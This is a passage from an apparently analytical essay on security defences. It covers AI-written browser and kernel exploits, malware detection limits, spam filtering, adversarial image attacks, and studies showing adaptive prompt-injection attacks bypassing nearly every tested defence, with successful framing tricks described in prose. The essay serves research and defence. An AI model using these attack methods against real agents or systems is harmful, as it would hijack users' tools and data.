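The models also tried to escape Firefox's sandbox by a method that Mozilla had already blocked. Objects in JavaScript inherit much of their behaviour from shared objects called prototypes, so an attacker who alters a prototype can change how many other objects behave. Researchers had escaped the sandbox several times by altering prototypes in the parent process. Rather than repair each case separately, Mozilla froze the prototypes by default so that nothing could alter them. This blocked the whole line of attack,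 including versions that nobody had yet tried. When Mozilla's engineers later read the logs of the AI search, they saw many attempts at this kind of escape, and the frozen prototypes had stopped them all.

Mythos Preview produced working exploits in 181 of 250 trials against flaws in Firefox's JavaScript engine, while an earlier Claude model produced two, according to Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked*. Each trial began with a known crash, and Anthropic had removed the browser's sandbox, so the trials measured how well the model can take over a renderer but not how well it can then escape the sandbox.

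### Chrome and the Linux kernel

Other tests kept the sandboxes in place. In April 2026 Carlini and colleagues reported that Mythos Preview had found flaws in every major browser. The web page mentioned earlier combined a browser exploit, a sandbox escape and an operating system flaw to let an attacker write to a visitor's kernel.

A later, unreleased model did similar work on Chrome. Anthropic's *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026) describes five attacks on widely used software, each of which needed little or no action from the victim. According to The Hacker News, the Chrome attack combined four flaws. The first two gave the attacker control of the renderer, the third revealed the privileged process's memory layout, and the last let the attacker run code outside the sandbox. By 20 October, Google had fixed all four, and Anthropic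 had reported 62 serious flaws in Chrome, including 13 sandbox escapes. Anthropic says the attacks needed little human involvement, but it has not published what its staff did at each step.

The Linux kernel withstood remote attacks for longer than local ones. Mythos Preview wrote nearly a dozen exploits that gave an ordinary user of a Linux computer administrator (root) access. It also found memory errors that an attacker could trigger remotely, but after several thousand scans it could not turn any of them into a working attack, which Carlini and colleagues attributed to the kernel's layered defences. About six months later, the newer model wrote a remote exploit that runs commands as root, without a login, on any unpatched server that accepts connections through multipath TCP, an optional feature. Developers patched that flaw on 15 October.

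Local attacks have become cheap to find. OpenAI's *A thousand fewer paths to root* describes a single run of the company's security model that validated 948 flaws through which an ordinary Linux user could gain greater privileges. The model also wrote a patch for each. *AI Agents Got Root on Linux via 948 Kernel Flaws* (Kovacs, 2026) reports that the agents built working exploits for about $1,280 per flaw. A tightly sandboxed program, such as a browser's renderer, probably cannot reach many of these flaws, because it can make only a few kinds of request to the kernel. Containers that can make more kinds are at greater risk.

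As a result, maintainers now fix nearly 2,000 recorded vulnerabilities in each Linux release, up from about 500, according to TechSpot (2026). This helps users who install the new releases, but attackers can study each published patch to learn which flaw remains on computers that lack it. Carlini and colleagues gave Mythos Preview a list of known Linux flaws and asked it to choose the 40 most promising and write exploits for them. It succeeded with more than half. One exploit, which combined several flaws, took less than a day and cost under $2,000.

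### Friction and hard barriers

Carlini and colleagues expect defences based on tedium to weaken against AI models, but they think "hard barriers", such as address randomisation and the W^X rule, will remain important.

Address randomisation loads the kernel at a different place in memory each time the computer starts. An attacker who can use a flaw to overwrite one location then does not know which location to choose. W^X, short for "write xor execute", allows a program to write to a region of memory or run code from it, but not both, so an attacker cannot write new code into memory and run it.

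Mythos Preview's exploits suggest that address randomisation slows attackers down but does not stop them. The model repeatedly got past it by using one flaw to read an address from the kernel's memory and another to overwrite the right place. In one case it needed no memory error to learn an address, because the kernel deliberately gave one to ordinary programs. There are also few positions to guess from, since Linux on ordinary PCs chooses among about 512 for its code, compared with 2^128 possible keys for AES. Attackers look for a leak instead of guessing mainly because a wrong guess is likely to crash the machine.

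W^X stops the technique it targets, but attackers found another long before language models existed. They rearrange fragments of code already in the program, as Mythos Preview did in its attack on FreeBSD.

Carlini and colleagues may have had a narrower distinction in mind. Without a leak, an attacker can't get past address randomisation by working harder and has to find another flaw. That difference is real, but it matters less when models can find the extra flaw easily. Randomisation is a hard barrier only if no part of a huge kernel ever reveals an address, and that assumption often fails. Microsoft treats randomised memory as defence in depth, which fits the evidence better.

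The browser sandbox falls somewhere in between. Its designers intend it as a real boundary, and a program inside cannot open a file through persistence alone. But the boundary holds only if a large privileged process and the reachable parts of the kernel contain no usable flaw, and Anthropic's 13 escapes from Chrome show that this is far from true. The sandbox makes attacks harder, but it depends on continual repairs, so it fails the third test of a win set out earlier. seL4 comes much closer to passing, because its assumptions cover far less code and much of that code is formally verified.

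### Mozilla's case for a decisive win

Mozilla's engineers are more hopeful about repairs. Mozilla's *The zero-days are numbered* describes how the company has worked around the clock since February with AI models to find and fix flaws. Bobby Holley, Firefox's chief technology officer, believes defenders "finally have a chance to win, decisively", according to The Next Web's *Mozilla patched 271 Firefox bugs found by Anthropic's Mythos*.

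Holley argues that attackers have the advantage when only experts can find subtle flaws, because an attacker can spend months looking for a single flaw while the defender lacks the resources to look everywhere. Inexpensive automated searches remove that advantage. Mozilla has not seen the models find a bug that an elite human researcher could not have found, and it argues that a well-organised program has a finite number of defects. This is the later part of the curve in Garfinkel and Dafoe's model, where the defender has the advantage.

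Evidence from Firefox supports part of this. Mozilla quickly reduced the number of flaws, with more than 100 people contributing code. But it acknowledges that it has not found all of the hidden bugs, and programmers add new ones as they write. Mozilla plans to have models scan each change before release, which would help keep the number of flaws from growing again. The argument also holds only if the defenders' models are about as good as the attackers'. A search that finds nothing shows only that one model can find no more flaws, and OpenAI reports that stronger models find more.

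Defenders may not keep their early access to such models either. Anthropic gave Mythos Preview to a restricted group of organisations so they could make repairs first. The Next Web reported that unauthorised users got in on the day of the announcement by guessing the model's web address through an outside supplier's system.

Help Net Security gives reasons to doubt that other projects can repeat Mozilla's success. It cites figures from Echo, a software supply chain company, on 27 published flaws that Mythos Preview found in open-source software. The model rated eight as critical, but outside scorers and the maintainers agreed with only one of those ratings. In some cases the model had overlooked that an attacker would already need privileged access. A team that fixed the flaws in the model's order would have started with several of the wrong ones. In Echo's July 2026 survey of more than 80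 senior security leaders in the US, 37% said the biggest obstacle to securing the software they depend on was finding more flaws than they could fix.

Firefox updates itself, so it can also deliver a repair to most of its users within days. Many routers, cameras and industrial machines run old versions of Linux that the manufacturers no longer update. A flaw that costs $1,280 to find and repair in the current kernel may never be repaired on those devices.

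## Malware, spam and adversarial images

Defenders have not won against malicious software (malware), spam or adversarial images, which are pictures with tiny changes meant to fool image classifiers. Antivirus companies have fought malware since the 1980s, mail providers still filter out billions of spam messages a day, and researchers have been trying to stop attacks on image classifiers for more than a decade. These three cases serve as a comparison group, because a feature shared by successful defences can help explain their success only if it is mostly missing where defenders have failed to win.

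### Why no program can detect every virus

A computer virus is a program that copies itself into other programs. In *Cure of Computer Viruses*, Fred Cohen (1984) proved that no detector can correctly decide, for every possible program, whether it is a virus. He assumed that such a detector exists and derived a contradiction.

1. Suppose that a detector, D, gives the right answer for every program.
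2. An attacker writes a program, CV, that contains a copy of D and uses it to examine CV itself.
3. If D answers "virus", CV infects nothing. If D answers "not a virus", CV infects other programs.
4. The answer "virus" is therefore wrong, because CV never infects anything. The answer "not a virus" is also wrong, because CV does.
5. D gives the wrong answer about CV, which contradicts the first step.

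Cohen's proof rules out only a perfect detector. A detector that flags every program as a virus will never miss one, and a detector that can return "unsure" can avoid mistakes. The Rust compiler has a similar limit, since no program can decide for every other program whether that program will use memory after freeing it. The compiler rejects any ordinary code it cannot show to be safe, including some harmless code, and the programmer rewrites it. An antivirus product cannot be so strict, because its users want to run software they did not write and cannot change. The theorem therefore does not fully explain why malware has been so hard to stop.

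### Signatures and learned detectors

Early antivirus products relied on signatures, patterns found in known malware. Cohen describes a virus whose first line is always 1234567. A defender can easily refuse to run any program that starts with this line, but the attacker can just as easily change it to 123456. Cohen also describes a virus that inserts random, meaningless statements each time it copies itself, so the copies look different but do the same damage.

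A detector can instead watch what a program does, but viruses use the same services as legitimate software. A compiler that compiles a new version of itself meets Cohen's definition of a virus, because it puts an evolved copy of itself into another program. The detector could raise an alarm when a program changes an unusual number of files, but an attacker who knows the threshold can stay below it.

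Learned detectors are trained on examples of malware and harmless software, so they can recognise some variants that nobody has catalogued. But malware authors can change almost anything about a program as long as it still does its job. Gilmer, Adams and colleagues (2018), in *Motivating the Rules of the Game for Adversarial Example Research*, note that sophisticated attackers already encrypt the harmful part of a virus and vary the code that decrypts it. Companies often use learned detectors while assuming that a motivated attacker can fool them. The detectors still help catch known malware from unsophisticated attackers and send suspicious files to the right experts.

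Malware detection fails the third test of a win because defenders must keep updating their detectors to catch new attacks. If attackers use a fixed method, defenders can collect samples and train a detector on them. Once the detector is on sale, attackers can buy a copy and alter their malware until it goes undetected.

### Asking who made the program

App signing and allowlists helped because they don't have to determine whether a program is harmful, so they can stop malware that nobody has seen before. With app signing, a developer attaches a digital signature to a program, and the device checks that the signature comes from an approved source and that nobody has altered the program since. An allowlist names the programs that may run and blocks all others. iPhones have relied on signing since Apple opened its App Store in 2008.

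In *Computer Viruses* (1987), Cohen described an early version of the idea. A system would keep a list of everyone who had affected each file, and a rule could require a trusted person to certify the file before others passed it on. Cohen also saw that cautious rules block some legitimate sharing and tend to push a system towards isolation. A company with a strict allowlist, for example, has to approve each new program before its employees can use it.

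With signing, whoever approves the software has to judge whether it is harmful. Apple's reviewers still have to decide whether an app is malicious, but they can do so once for all users and withdraw approval later. Reviewers can also be fooled. In 2015 attackers circulated an altered copy of Apple's programming tools that added hidden code to the apps built with it, including the messaging app WeChat. The developers signed the apps without noticing the code, and Apple approved them.

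An allowlist also gives little protection if an approved program can run code from elsewhere. Cohen pointed out that someone can write a virus in the programming language Basic even if nobody can alter the program that runs Basic code. Office software that runs small programs hidden in documents has the same weakness.

### How spam became tolerable

A mail provider can learn from an entire spam campaign, while each recipient sees only a few of its messages. When a Gmail user marks a message as spam, Google uses the report to catch similar messages sent to others. This works against bulk spammers because they have to send many messages, and each one gives the filter more evidence.

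According to Google's *Email that keeps your private information safe*, Gmail blocks nearly 10 million spam emails a minute, and more than 99.9% of spam, phishing attempts and malware. (Phishing messages impersonate someone the recipient trusts, often to steal a password.) If both figures cover the same mail, up to about 10,000 unwanted messages get through each minute, or 14 million a day. The number may be higher, since Google cannot count spam that neither its filter nor any user has recognised.

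The filters are also improving. Google's *Email scams surge over the holiday* reports that users saw 35% fewer scams in the first month of one holiday season than a year earlier. A language model trained on spam, phishing and malware blocked 20% more spam than before.

Sender authentication helps by answering a narrower question than whether a message is spam. Email was designed without any check on the sender's address, so anyone could claim to write from a bank. Three standards now provide one:

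- SPF lets the owner of a domain, such as a bank's web address, publish a list of the servers that may send its mail.
- DKIM adds a digital signature that the receiving server can check.
- DMARC checks that the domain verified by SPF or DKIM matches the one shown to the reader, and lets the owner say what should happen to messages that fail.

In February 2024, Google began requiring bulk senders to authenticate their mail to Gmail users. According to Google's figures, this reduced unauthenticated messages by 65%, or 265 billion fewer messages in 2024. The figures are cited in *Google stats show why DMARC and email authentication matter* by Valimail, which sells authentication services.

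A spammer can still register a new domain and authenticate its mail, but the domain then builds up its own reputation. Suped, a company that helps businesses get their email delivered, reports that Gmail advises senders to keep user complaints below 0.1% of messages and never let them reach 0.3%. Gmail began enforcing its rules more strictly in November 2025 and may now reject mail that breaks them.

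These measures work partly because spammers have thin margins. In 2008 researchers in California secretly diverted part of a spam network's traffic to their own copy of its online pharmacy, which took no payments. Almost 350 million messages led to 28 attempted purchases, worth about $2,700. Revenue would have been about $8 per million messages sent, so a spammer with higher costs would have lost money. If filters had then let through only a tenth as many messages, revenue would have fallen to about 80 cents per million sent, so a filter can ruin a spammer's business without stopping every message.

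### When blocking 99.9% is enough

A high average block rate is enough against most advertising spam, because each message that gets through does little harm and the spammer needs many successes to profit. The average is a much less useful measure of protection against a targeted attacker, who may need only one employee to open one message.

Suppose that each attempt has a probability p of getting through and that the attempts are independent. The chance that at least one of k attempts succeeds is

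P = 1 − (1 − p)^k

If each attempt succeeds with probability p = 0.001, an attacker has a 63% chance of at least one success in 1,000 attempts and a 95% chance in 3,000.

Real attackers can do better than this because they learn from their failures. An attacker can open a Gmail account, send test messages to it until one reaches the inbox, and then send only that version to the victim. The victim's filter never receives the failed attempts, so it cannot learn from them or block the sender.

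The average also does not show how well a filter blocks each kind of message. If one unwanted message in 10,000 were a carefully written attack on a particular person, a filter could miss every such attack and still block 99.99% of unwanted mail. Blocking most unwanted mail makes spam tolerable, but organisations need other protection against targeted phishing, such as login methods that do not rely on a password someone can steal.

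### Fooling an image classifier

An image classifier is a program, today usually a neural network, that assigns a label such as "cat" to a picture. An adversarial example is an input that an attacker designed to make a classifier mislabel it. In the best-known kind, the attacker takes a picture the classifier labels correctly and changes it so slightly that a person sees no difference.

Let x be the picture, y its correct label and δ the attacker's change. The loss L measures how wrong the model's answer is. The attacker looks for the change that

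maximises L(x + δ, y), with |δᵢ| ≤ ε for every i

Each i is one colour value of one pixel, and ε is the largest change allowed. A common limit is 8/255, which means that each colour value, on a scale from 0 to 255, may move by at most 8. The standard method, called projected gradient descent, repeats the following step:

xₜ₊₁ = Proj(xₜ + α × sign(∇L(xₜ, y)))

1. The attacker calculates the gradient, ∇L, which shows whether raising or lowering each colour value would make the model's answer worse.
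2. The attacker moves every value a small distance, α, in the harmful direction.
3. The function Proj moves any value that has gone too far back within the limit.

Small adversarial changes to an image have a large effect because they all push the model's output in the same direction. Suppose a simple model multiplies each of the 3,072 colour values in a small picture by a weight and adds up the results. If the weights are of equal size, coordinated changes shift the total about 55 times (the square root of 3,072) as far as random changes of the same size, which mostly cancel out. Neural networks are more complicated, but they have a similar weakness.

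### How researchers broke the defences

Early defences often hid the gradient from the attacker without removing the model's errors. In *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (2018), Athalye, Carlini and Wagner examined nine defences accepted at that year's ICLR, a leading machine learning conference. All nine claimed to withstand attackers with full access to the model, but seven depended on making the gradient unusable. They broke six of those seven completely and the other partly.

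Some defences first cleaned the picture with a step that has no useful gradient. Since the cleaned picture looks much like the original, the attackers ran the cleaning step as usual but ignored it when calculating the gradient. This gradient was inexact, but good enough to find an adversarial example after many iterations. Other defences altered each picture at random, and the attackers averaged the gradient over many random versions.

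Researchers then began to test their defences against adaptive attackers, but often not thoroughly enough. Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues (*On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses*, 2020) selected 13 defences from leading conferences and bypassed all of them, although almost all had already faced some kind of adaptive attack. Many of the earlier tests had reused an attack built for another defence. The team's attacks were simpler than those in the papers that proposed the defences, but no single strategy worked against every defence. Nasr and colleagues later found the same pattern in defences for language models.

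Adversarial training withstood attacks better. It generates attack pictures while the model is learning and trains the model to label them correctly. In Athalye and colleagues' tests, a model trained this way still labelled 47% of attacked pictures correctly on CIFAR-10, a standard set of small pictures in ten categories.

### Robust accuracy today

Robust accuracy is the share of pictures that a model still labels correctly under attack. *VanillaBench* (Bunzel, 2026) gives the figures below for the most robust models on RobustBench, a public leaderboard that tests models with a standard set of four attacks. The CIFAR-100 dataset has 100 categories and ImageNet has 1,000.

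| Test set | Limit on each change | Robust accuracy | Same model, no attack | Best ordinary model, no attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10 | 8/255 | 75.28% | 93.6% | 99.5% |
| CIFAR-100 | 8/255 | 44.78% | 75.13% | 96.08% |
| ImageNet | 4/255 | 62.12% | 78.80% | 91.0% |

An attacker can therefore make the best CIFAR-10 model mislabel about one picture in four, compared with one in 16 without an attack. Robustness also reduces accuracy on ordinary pictures. Part of the gap between robust and standard models comes from differences in design, but Bunzel still finds an average loss of 3.5 to 17.5 percentage points when comparing models of the same or similar design. The newest model on the leaderboard dates from 2024.

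More computing power alone may not solve the problem. In *Adversarial Robustness Limits via Scaling-Law and Human-Alignment Studies*, Bartoldson, Diffenderfer and colleagues (2024) trained models of many sizes and extrapolated from the results. They predicted that robust accuracy on CIFAR-10 would level off near 90%, and that matching human performance would take about 10^30 calculations, or roughly 3,000 years on 25,000 of the leading chips of the time. Better training methods could reduce the amount of computation needed.

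In their small study, people also scored about 90%. Roughly a tenth of the attacked pictures had changed so much that the original label no longer fitted. A picture of a horse, for instance, might no longer look like one, but the benchmark still counts "horse" as the only correct answer, so part of the remaining error comes from the test itself.

Attacks of this kind also work on commercial AI systems. *Laundering AI Authority with Adversarial Examples* (Zhang, Peetathawatchai and colleagues, 2026) used projected gradient descent on publicly available image models to alter pictures, then tested them on GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6, Gemini 3 and Grok 4.2. Across hundreds of attempts to disguise a person's identity or get sexual content past a filter, success rates ranged from 22% to 100%, depending on the model and the task. In another demonstration, a model mistook the picture for something else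 and approved a drug that causes birth defects as safe during pregnancy. Training a model to refuse harmful requests does not help here, because the model misperceives the image and answers accordingly. A real attacker could also try several pictures in private and publish only one that works.

### Proofs about small changes

Certified robustness replaces testing with a mathematical guarantee that no change below a given size can alter the model's answer. One method limits how fast the model's output can change. Suppose that a model chooses between two labels according to whether its output f(x) is positive or negative. Its Lipschitz constant, K, is the most that the output can change per unit of change in the picture. The label is then safe within the radius

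r = |f(x)| / K

If f(x) is 0.6 and K is 1, no change smaller than 0.6 can move the output past zero. Here, the size of a change is the square root of the sum of the squared changes to all colour values, each on a scale from 0 to 1.

It is hard to keep K small in a deep network. Multiplying the constants of all the layers gives an upper limit on K for the whole network. With 30 layers that each have a constant of 1.2, the limit is about 237, and the guaranteed radius in the example shrinks from 0.6 to 0.0025. *LipNeXt* (Hu, Hu and Fredrikson, 2026) keeps K at 1 by building the network from operations that never increase the distance between two inputs. According to *Lipschitz Thinking* (Brau, Piras and colleagues, 2026), such a network can produce a certificate in a single run.

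Another method, randomised smoothing, adds random noise to many copies of the picture and takes the most common answer. A small change to the picture can shift only a limited share of the answers, so it cannot overturn a clear majority. The guarantee has a small chance of being wrong because it relies on a sample of noisy copies. *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019) used this method to certify correct answers for 49% of ImageNet pictures at a radius of 0.5.

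Hu and colleagues' largest network certifies 41.2% of ImageNet pictures at a radius of 36/255 (about 0.14). A version trained for a radius of 1 certifies 22.4% and labels 41.0% correctly when nobody attacks. Even a radius of 1 is small. A change of that size, spread evenly over a standard ImageNet picture of 224 by 224 pixels, would alter each colour value by less than one step out of 255, whereas an attacker on RobustBench may change each value by up to four steps.

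A certificate rules out attacks that make only small changes to an image, but attackers can make larger ones. Gilmer and colleagues point out that moving a picture sideways by one pixel hardly affects how it looks, but counts as a large change by these measures. People who illegally stream boxing matches crop the picture or film a television screen, and their viewers don't mind. An attacker can also make a self-driving car miss a stop sign by knocking the sign over.

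A certificate also does not guarantee that the label is right. *Advances in adversarial attacks and defenses in computer vision* (2021) cites the Shadow Attack on certified models. It makes large, smooth changes to an image, like a shadow falling across it, that take the image outside the range of the original guarantee. The model can then give the wrong label with a valid certificate, because the certificate guarantees only that small further changes would not alter that label.

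In 2018 Gilmer and colleagues objected that they could not find a convincing real attack that required an invisible change. Zhang and colleagues' attacks weaken that objection, because a user who sees an ordinary picture has little reason to doubt the AI system's answer. Certificates for small changes would be more useful here, but an attacker could still choose a different picture or a less subtle change.

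### No exact definition of a bad input

In all three cases the defender has to classify inputs as good or bad without an exact definition of bad. A support technician and a thief can use the same program to control someone's computer remotely. Some people want a newsletter that others consider spam. The correct label for a picture depends on what people see in it, and they do not always agree. By contrast, software can check exactly whether an input stays within its place in a database query or a write stays within its array.

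As well as being exact, a useful definition has to be one that a computer can check, and it has to cover the harm the defender wants to prevent. Cohen defined a virus precisely, but no program can recognise every virus, and the definition includes some legitimate compilers. Certified robustness has an exact definition that a computer can check, but it leaves out most of what an attacker can do to a picture. App signing and sender authentication let a computer check where a program or message came from, but a trusted source can still send something harmful.

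## Training and filtering against prompt injection

Most defences against prompt injection involve writing prompts that separate the user's request from outside content, training models to ignore injected commands, or using a second model to screen incoming text. All of these share a difficulty with spam filters, which is that nobody has an exact definition of what to block. The instruction "Forward this invoice to accounts" is harmless in one email and an attack in another. By late 2026 the best models resisted most single attempts, but attackers who could adapt and try again still succeeded much more often.

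### Marking, training and screening

The simplest defences change only the prompt. In Spotlighting, the developer separates trusted from untrusted text with markers and tells the model what the markers mean. In prompt sandwiching, the developer repeats the user's request after the outside content, so the model reads it last. According to Nasr and colleagues, both methods are based on the assumption that an injection works by distracting the model from the user's task. They also depend on the model giving the markers or the reminder more weight than anything the attacker writes.

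Other developers train the model on examples of attacks. The creators of StruQ gave a model requests whose accompanying data contained an injection, and trained it to respond as if the injection were absent. He, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PIPETTE*, write the goal of such training as making this quantity small:

Loss = −Σ log π(aₜ | Hₜ′)

Here aₜ is the action the model took at step t when the content was clean, Hₜ′ is the same history with an injection added, and π(aₜ | Hₜ′) is the probability that the model still takes that action. SecAlign instead uses pairs of responses, one that does what the user asked and one that follows the injection, and trains the model to favour the first. Meta-SecAlign, a version of Meta's Llama model with 70 billion parameters, uses the same approach.

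Developers can also let the agent attempt attacked tasks and reward it afterwards. He and colleagues describe a reward of

r = U × (1 − A)

where U is 1 if the agent finishes the user's task and A is 1 if it carries out the attacker's. Both are otherwise 0. An agent that stops work whenever it meets suspicious text earns nothing, because the user still needs the honest part of the email or web page. All these kinds of training assume that lessons from the attacks in the training set carry over to attacks that nobody has written yet.

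A detector is a separate classifier that screens content before the agent uses it, or checks the agent's output. PromptGuard, PIGuard and Protect AI's detector are small language models trained on harmless prompts and known attacks. Google sells a similar service called Model Armor. Detectors rely on injections looking different from ordinary text.

Two other defences rely on a hidden test. Data Sentinel instructs a model to repeat a secret word while ignoring the outside content, and treats the content as dangerous if the model doesn't repeat the word. MELON runs the agent a second time, replacing the user's request with a request to summarise the content. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, the content probably caused the call, not the user's request. Both tests are much weaker against an attacker who knows about them, so they fall short of Kerckhoffs's principle.

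### The AgentDojo benchmark

Researchers often test these defences on AgentDojo, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2024. It simulates office software, a Slack chat system, a travel service and a bank, and gives the agent 97 ordinary tasks. An attack test pairs one of these tasks with an attacker's goal and places the attacker's text in something the agent will read. In one test, the user asks who is attending an event, and the attacker has put text in the calendar entry to make the agent email a stranger. Software then checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal.

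The benchmark measures usefulness as well as security, because an agent that refuses to send any email would resist this attack but be a poor assistant. AgentDojo includes only fixed attack texts, which recent defences were quickly able to defeat, but researchers can add their own.

### Twelve defences against adaptive attackers

Nasr and colleagues used AgentDojo for most of their work on prompt injection. They released their study in October 2025 and presented it at the USENIX Security conference in 2026. It covered the eight injection defences named above that they could test on AgentDojo or similar benchmarks, as well as StruQ, Data Sentinel and two defences against jailbreaks.

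 They attacked each one with some version of the same loop:

1. Write one or more candidate texts.
2. Run them against the defended system and score the results.
3. Keep the most promising ones.
4. Use the scores and the system's responses to write better candidates.

The team ran this loop in four ways. Gradient attacks work like those on image classifiers, but they are less reliable on words than on pixels. With reinforcement learning, an attacking model writes the texts and is trained to produce more like those that score well. In the search attack, one language model rewrites the best earlier texts and another scores the results from 1 to 10. The fourth method was an online contest with $20,000 in prizes and more than 500 participants.

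The table gives the search attack's results on 80 AgentDojo pairings, with Gemini 2.5 Pro running the agent. The fixed attack is a standard text that comes with AgentDojo. The search had up to 800 tries per pairing, and the last column counts only the pairings where it succeeded.

| Defence | Ordinary tasks completed, no attack | Fixed attack succeeds | Search attack succeeds | Median tries to first success |
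|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74% | 30% | 100% | 13 |
| Spotlighting | 75% | 28% | 99% | 14 |
| Prompt sandwiching | 73% | 21% | 95% | 14 |
| PromptGuard | 72% | 26% | 94% | 21 |
| Model Armor | 59% | 28% | 90% | 22 |
| Protect AI | 39% | 15% | 90% | 30 |
| MELON | 58% | 0% | 89% | 20 |
| PIGuard | 39% | 0% | 71% | 46 |

PIGuard resisted attacks best, but with it the agent completed barely half as many ordinary tasks as it did without a defence. Detectors can cause this by discarding harmless content that the agent needs.

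The gap between fixed and adaptive attacks was even wider on other models. On Meta-SecAlign, fixed attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time against Spotlighting and 4% against sandwiching, while the search succeeded 99% of the time against both. On three of the four models tested, the search succeeded at least 95% of the time against both prompting defences. On the fourth, GPT-5 Mini, it succeeded 47% of the time against Spotlighting and 69% against sandwiching, compared with 75% with no defence. Nasr and colleagues expect that a larger budget would raise these rates too.

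Training on known attacks did no better. Meta-SecAlign reported a 2% success rate for AgentDojo's fixed attacks, but the search raised it to 96%. The attack trained by reinforcement learning succeeded against StruQ in every case. This matches what happened with image classifiers, where training helped only when researchers generated new attacks against the model as it learned.

Many of the successful texts presented the attacker's task as a routine step in the user's task, such as logging a request before opening a file, rather than telling the agent to ignore its user. Repeating the user's request does not help against this, because the extra step appears to be part of the request. Detectors also have little to flag, since real offices send messages like these. Attacks on StruQ often imitated the system's own instructions. Against MELON, the search succeeded 76% of the time on one model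 when the attacker did not know how the defence worked. When the attacker did know, it wrote instructions that applied only when the agent was not summarising, and the rate rose to 95%.

Human contestants did even better than the search. They won all 40 challenges and produced 265 successful attacks on Spotlighting and 178 on sandwiching. On the 29 scenarios that both people and the search attempted, the search succeeded in 69%, while the contestants together succeeded in all of them. Among the contestants who tried all 29, the best succeeded in 75%.

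Zhan, Fang and colleagues had already bypassed eight defences in *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents* (2025), with a success rate above 50% against each one.

### Limits of the study

Nasr and colleagues tested whether each defence could be broken, not how much effort that would take. They assumed an attacker with a lot of computing power, and they gave their search for attacks each detector's confidence score, which a real attacker might not have. Even so, the search usually stopped improving after only 100 to 200 tries, and the median successful attack on Gemini 2.5 Pro took fewer than 50 with any of the defences.

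The team also chose its attacks for one defence at a time, whereas companies often combine several. The tests on Meta-SecAlign partly address this limitation, because they add a prompt or a detector to a model already trained to resist injections. The search still succeeded 64% to 99% of the time against these combinations. None of the tests included the monitoring and account bans that a company might use against someone who keeps trying.

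The success rates cannot be used to rank the defences, because the tests differed. The team followed each defence's original evaluation where it could, so it tested StruQ against attempts to make a model print a chosen phrase and Meta-SecAlign against attempts to make an agent misuse its tools. The team also left out defences that fix an agent's plan before it reads outside content, because the attacks could not have worked against them in most of the chosen scenarios.

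### Training on a larger set of attacks

Developers have responded by automatically generating attacks to train against, as OpenAI does for its browser agent. But He and colleagues found cases where a program that discovered more successful attacks did not produce a safer agent.

They ran two published attack generators against Qwen3-4B, a small open model, on 560 practice tasks. PISmith succeeded on 69% of the tasks and yielded 7,132 successful attack texts, while RL-Hammer succeeded on 33% and yielded 4,282. They then used reinforcement learning to train one copy of the model on each collection, and tested both copies with three kinds of attack that neither had seen in training. The strongest attack hijacked the copy trained on PISmith's larger collection in 47.5% of tasks and the copy trained on RL-Hammer's in 27.5%.

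The larger collection also produced the weaker agent in two of three other setups, which used a second model or a different kind of training. The differences are less striking as counts, because the test had only 40 tasks. The main comparison was 19 hijacked tasks against 11, and the gaps in the other two setups where the larger collection did worse were one task and two tasks. Zorz (2026) points out in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* that the team had also picked tasks on which simple attacks had already worked. The study showed that the number of attacks is a poor guide to their value, but not that training on attacks is worse than no training.

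He and colleagues think the generators kept repeating themselves. Once a generator finds a trick that works, such as claiming that the user's task is already finished, it can earn more reward by reusing that trick than by looking for another. Training encourages both generators to vary their attacks, but it measures variety by wording, so RL-Hammer could score well by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant text.

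PIPETTE, the team's alternative, measures variety by technique:

1. A language model describes how each successful text redirects the agent.
2. The system reduces thousands of these descriptions to a list of basic techniques.
3. A grader rates how fully the known techniques explain each new attack.
4. The generator earns an extra reward for attacks that succeed and that the list explains poorly.

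For Qwen3-4B, the techniques in RL-Hammer's collection scored about 0.20 on a scale from 0 to 1 for how well they explained a set of unseen attacks, while those in PIPETTE's scored about 0.60. Automated attackers that rewrote their texts over roughly 250 tries hijacked the resulting agents in at most 10% of the 40 tasks. The agents have not yet been tested in the kind of contest in which human attackers beat every defence.

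Training can also make an agent less useful. Llama-3.1-8B, the other model in the comparison, completed 40% of ordinary tasks before training and about 16% after supervised training on either collection, probably because it had learned to abandon tasks when the input contained text that sounded like an order. PIPETTE's training avoided this on Qwen3-4B, which completed 62% of ordinary tasks before training and 65% after.

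### Fifteen rounds with a frontier model

Larger models withstand a single attempt much better, so recent benchmarks give the attacker several. In *Adaptive Adversaries* (Jain, Hartmann and Li, 2026), Claude Opus 4.6, GPT-5.4 and Gemini 2.5 Pro attacked one another in 21 scenarios. The attacker had up to 15 rounds and could read the defender's earlier answers, while the defender began each round with no memory of earlier ones, like an agent that opens every email in a new session.

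In the first round, attacks never succeeded against Opus or GPT-5.4, and succeeded 1.0% of the time against Gemini. After 15 rounds, the success rates were 7.9% against Opus, 9.5% against GPT-5.4 and 16.8% against Gemini, and still rising. Learning from earlier attempts mattered more than the number of attempts. In a separate test on three scenarios, attackers who could see their earlier attempts won 13 of 36 battles, while attackers who had as many attempts but couldn't see them won none.

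The models had different weaknesses. Opus refused a direct request for a password but later included it in an explanation of how to encode a database address. Gemini accepted a forged change to a reviewer's score. Jain and colleagues then added a paragraph telling the defender to trust its original task over later text that contradicted it. The attacks' success rate across six scenarios fell from 41% to 26%. The paragraph stopped all the attacks in two scenarios that relied on false authority, but did nothing to protect the password. A prompt can therefore stop a particular kind of attack even when the attacker adapts. However, these defenders had no tools, and the attackers had far fewer tries than in Nasr and colleagues' search.

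### Attack success rates in 2026

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports similarly mixed results from a public contest in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against tool-using agents built on 13 models. To win, an attacker usually had to make the agent take a harmful action without revealing it in the reply to the user. Success rates per attempt ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Contestants could read the whole conversation before writing their attacks, which real attackers rarely can. A few attack templates worked widely, and one that described the conversation as a simulation succeeded in 21 of the 41 scenarios and against nine models.

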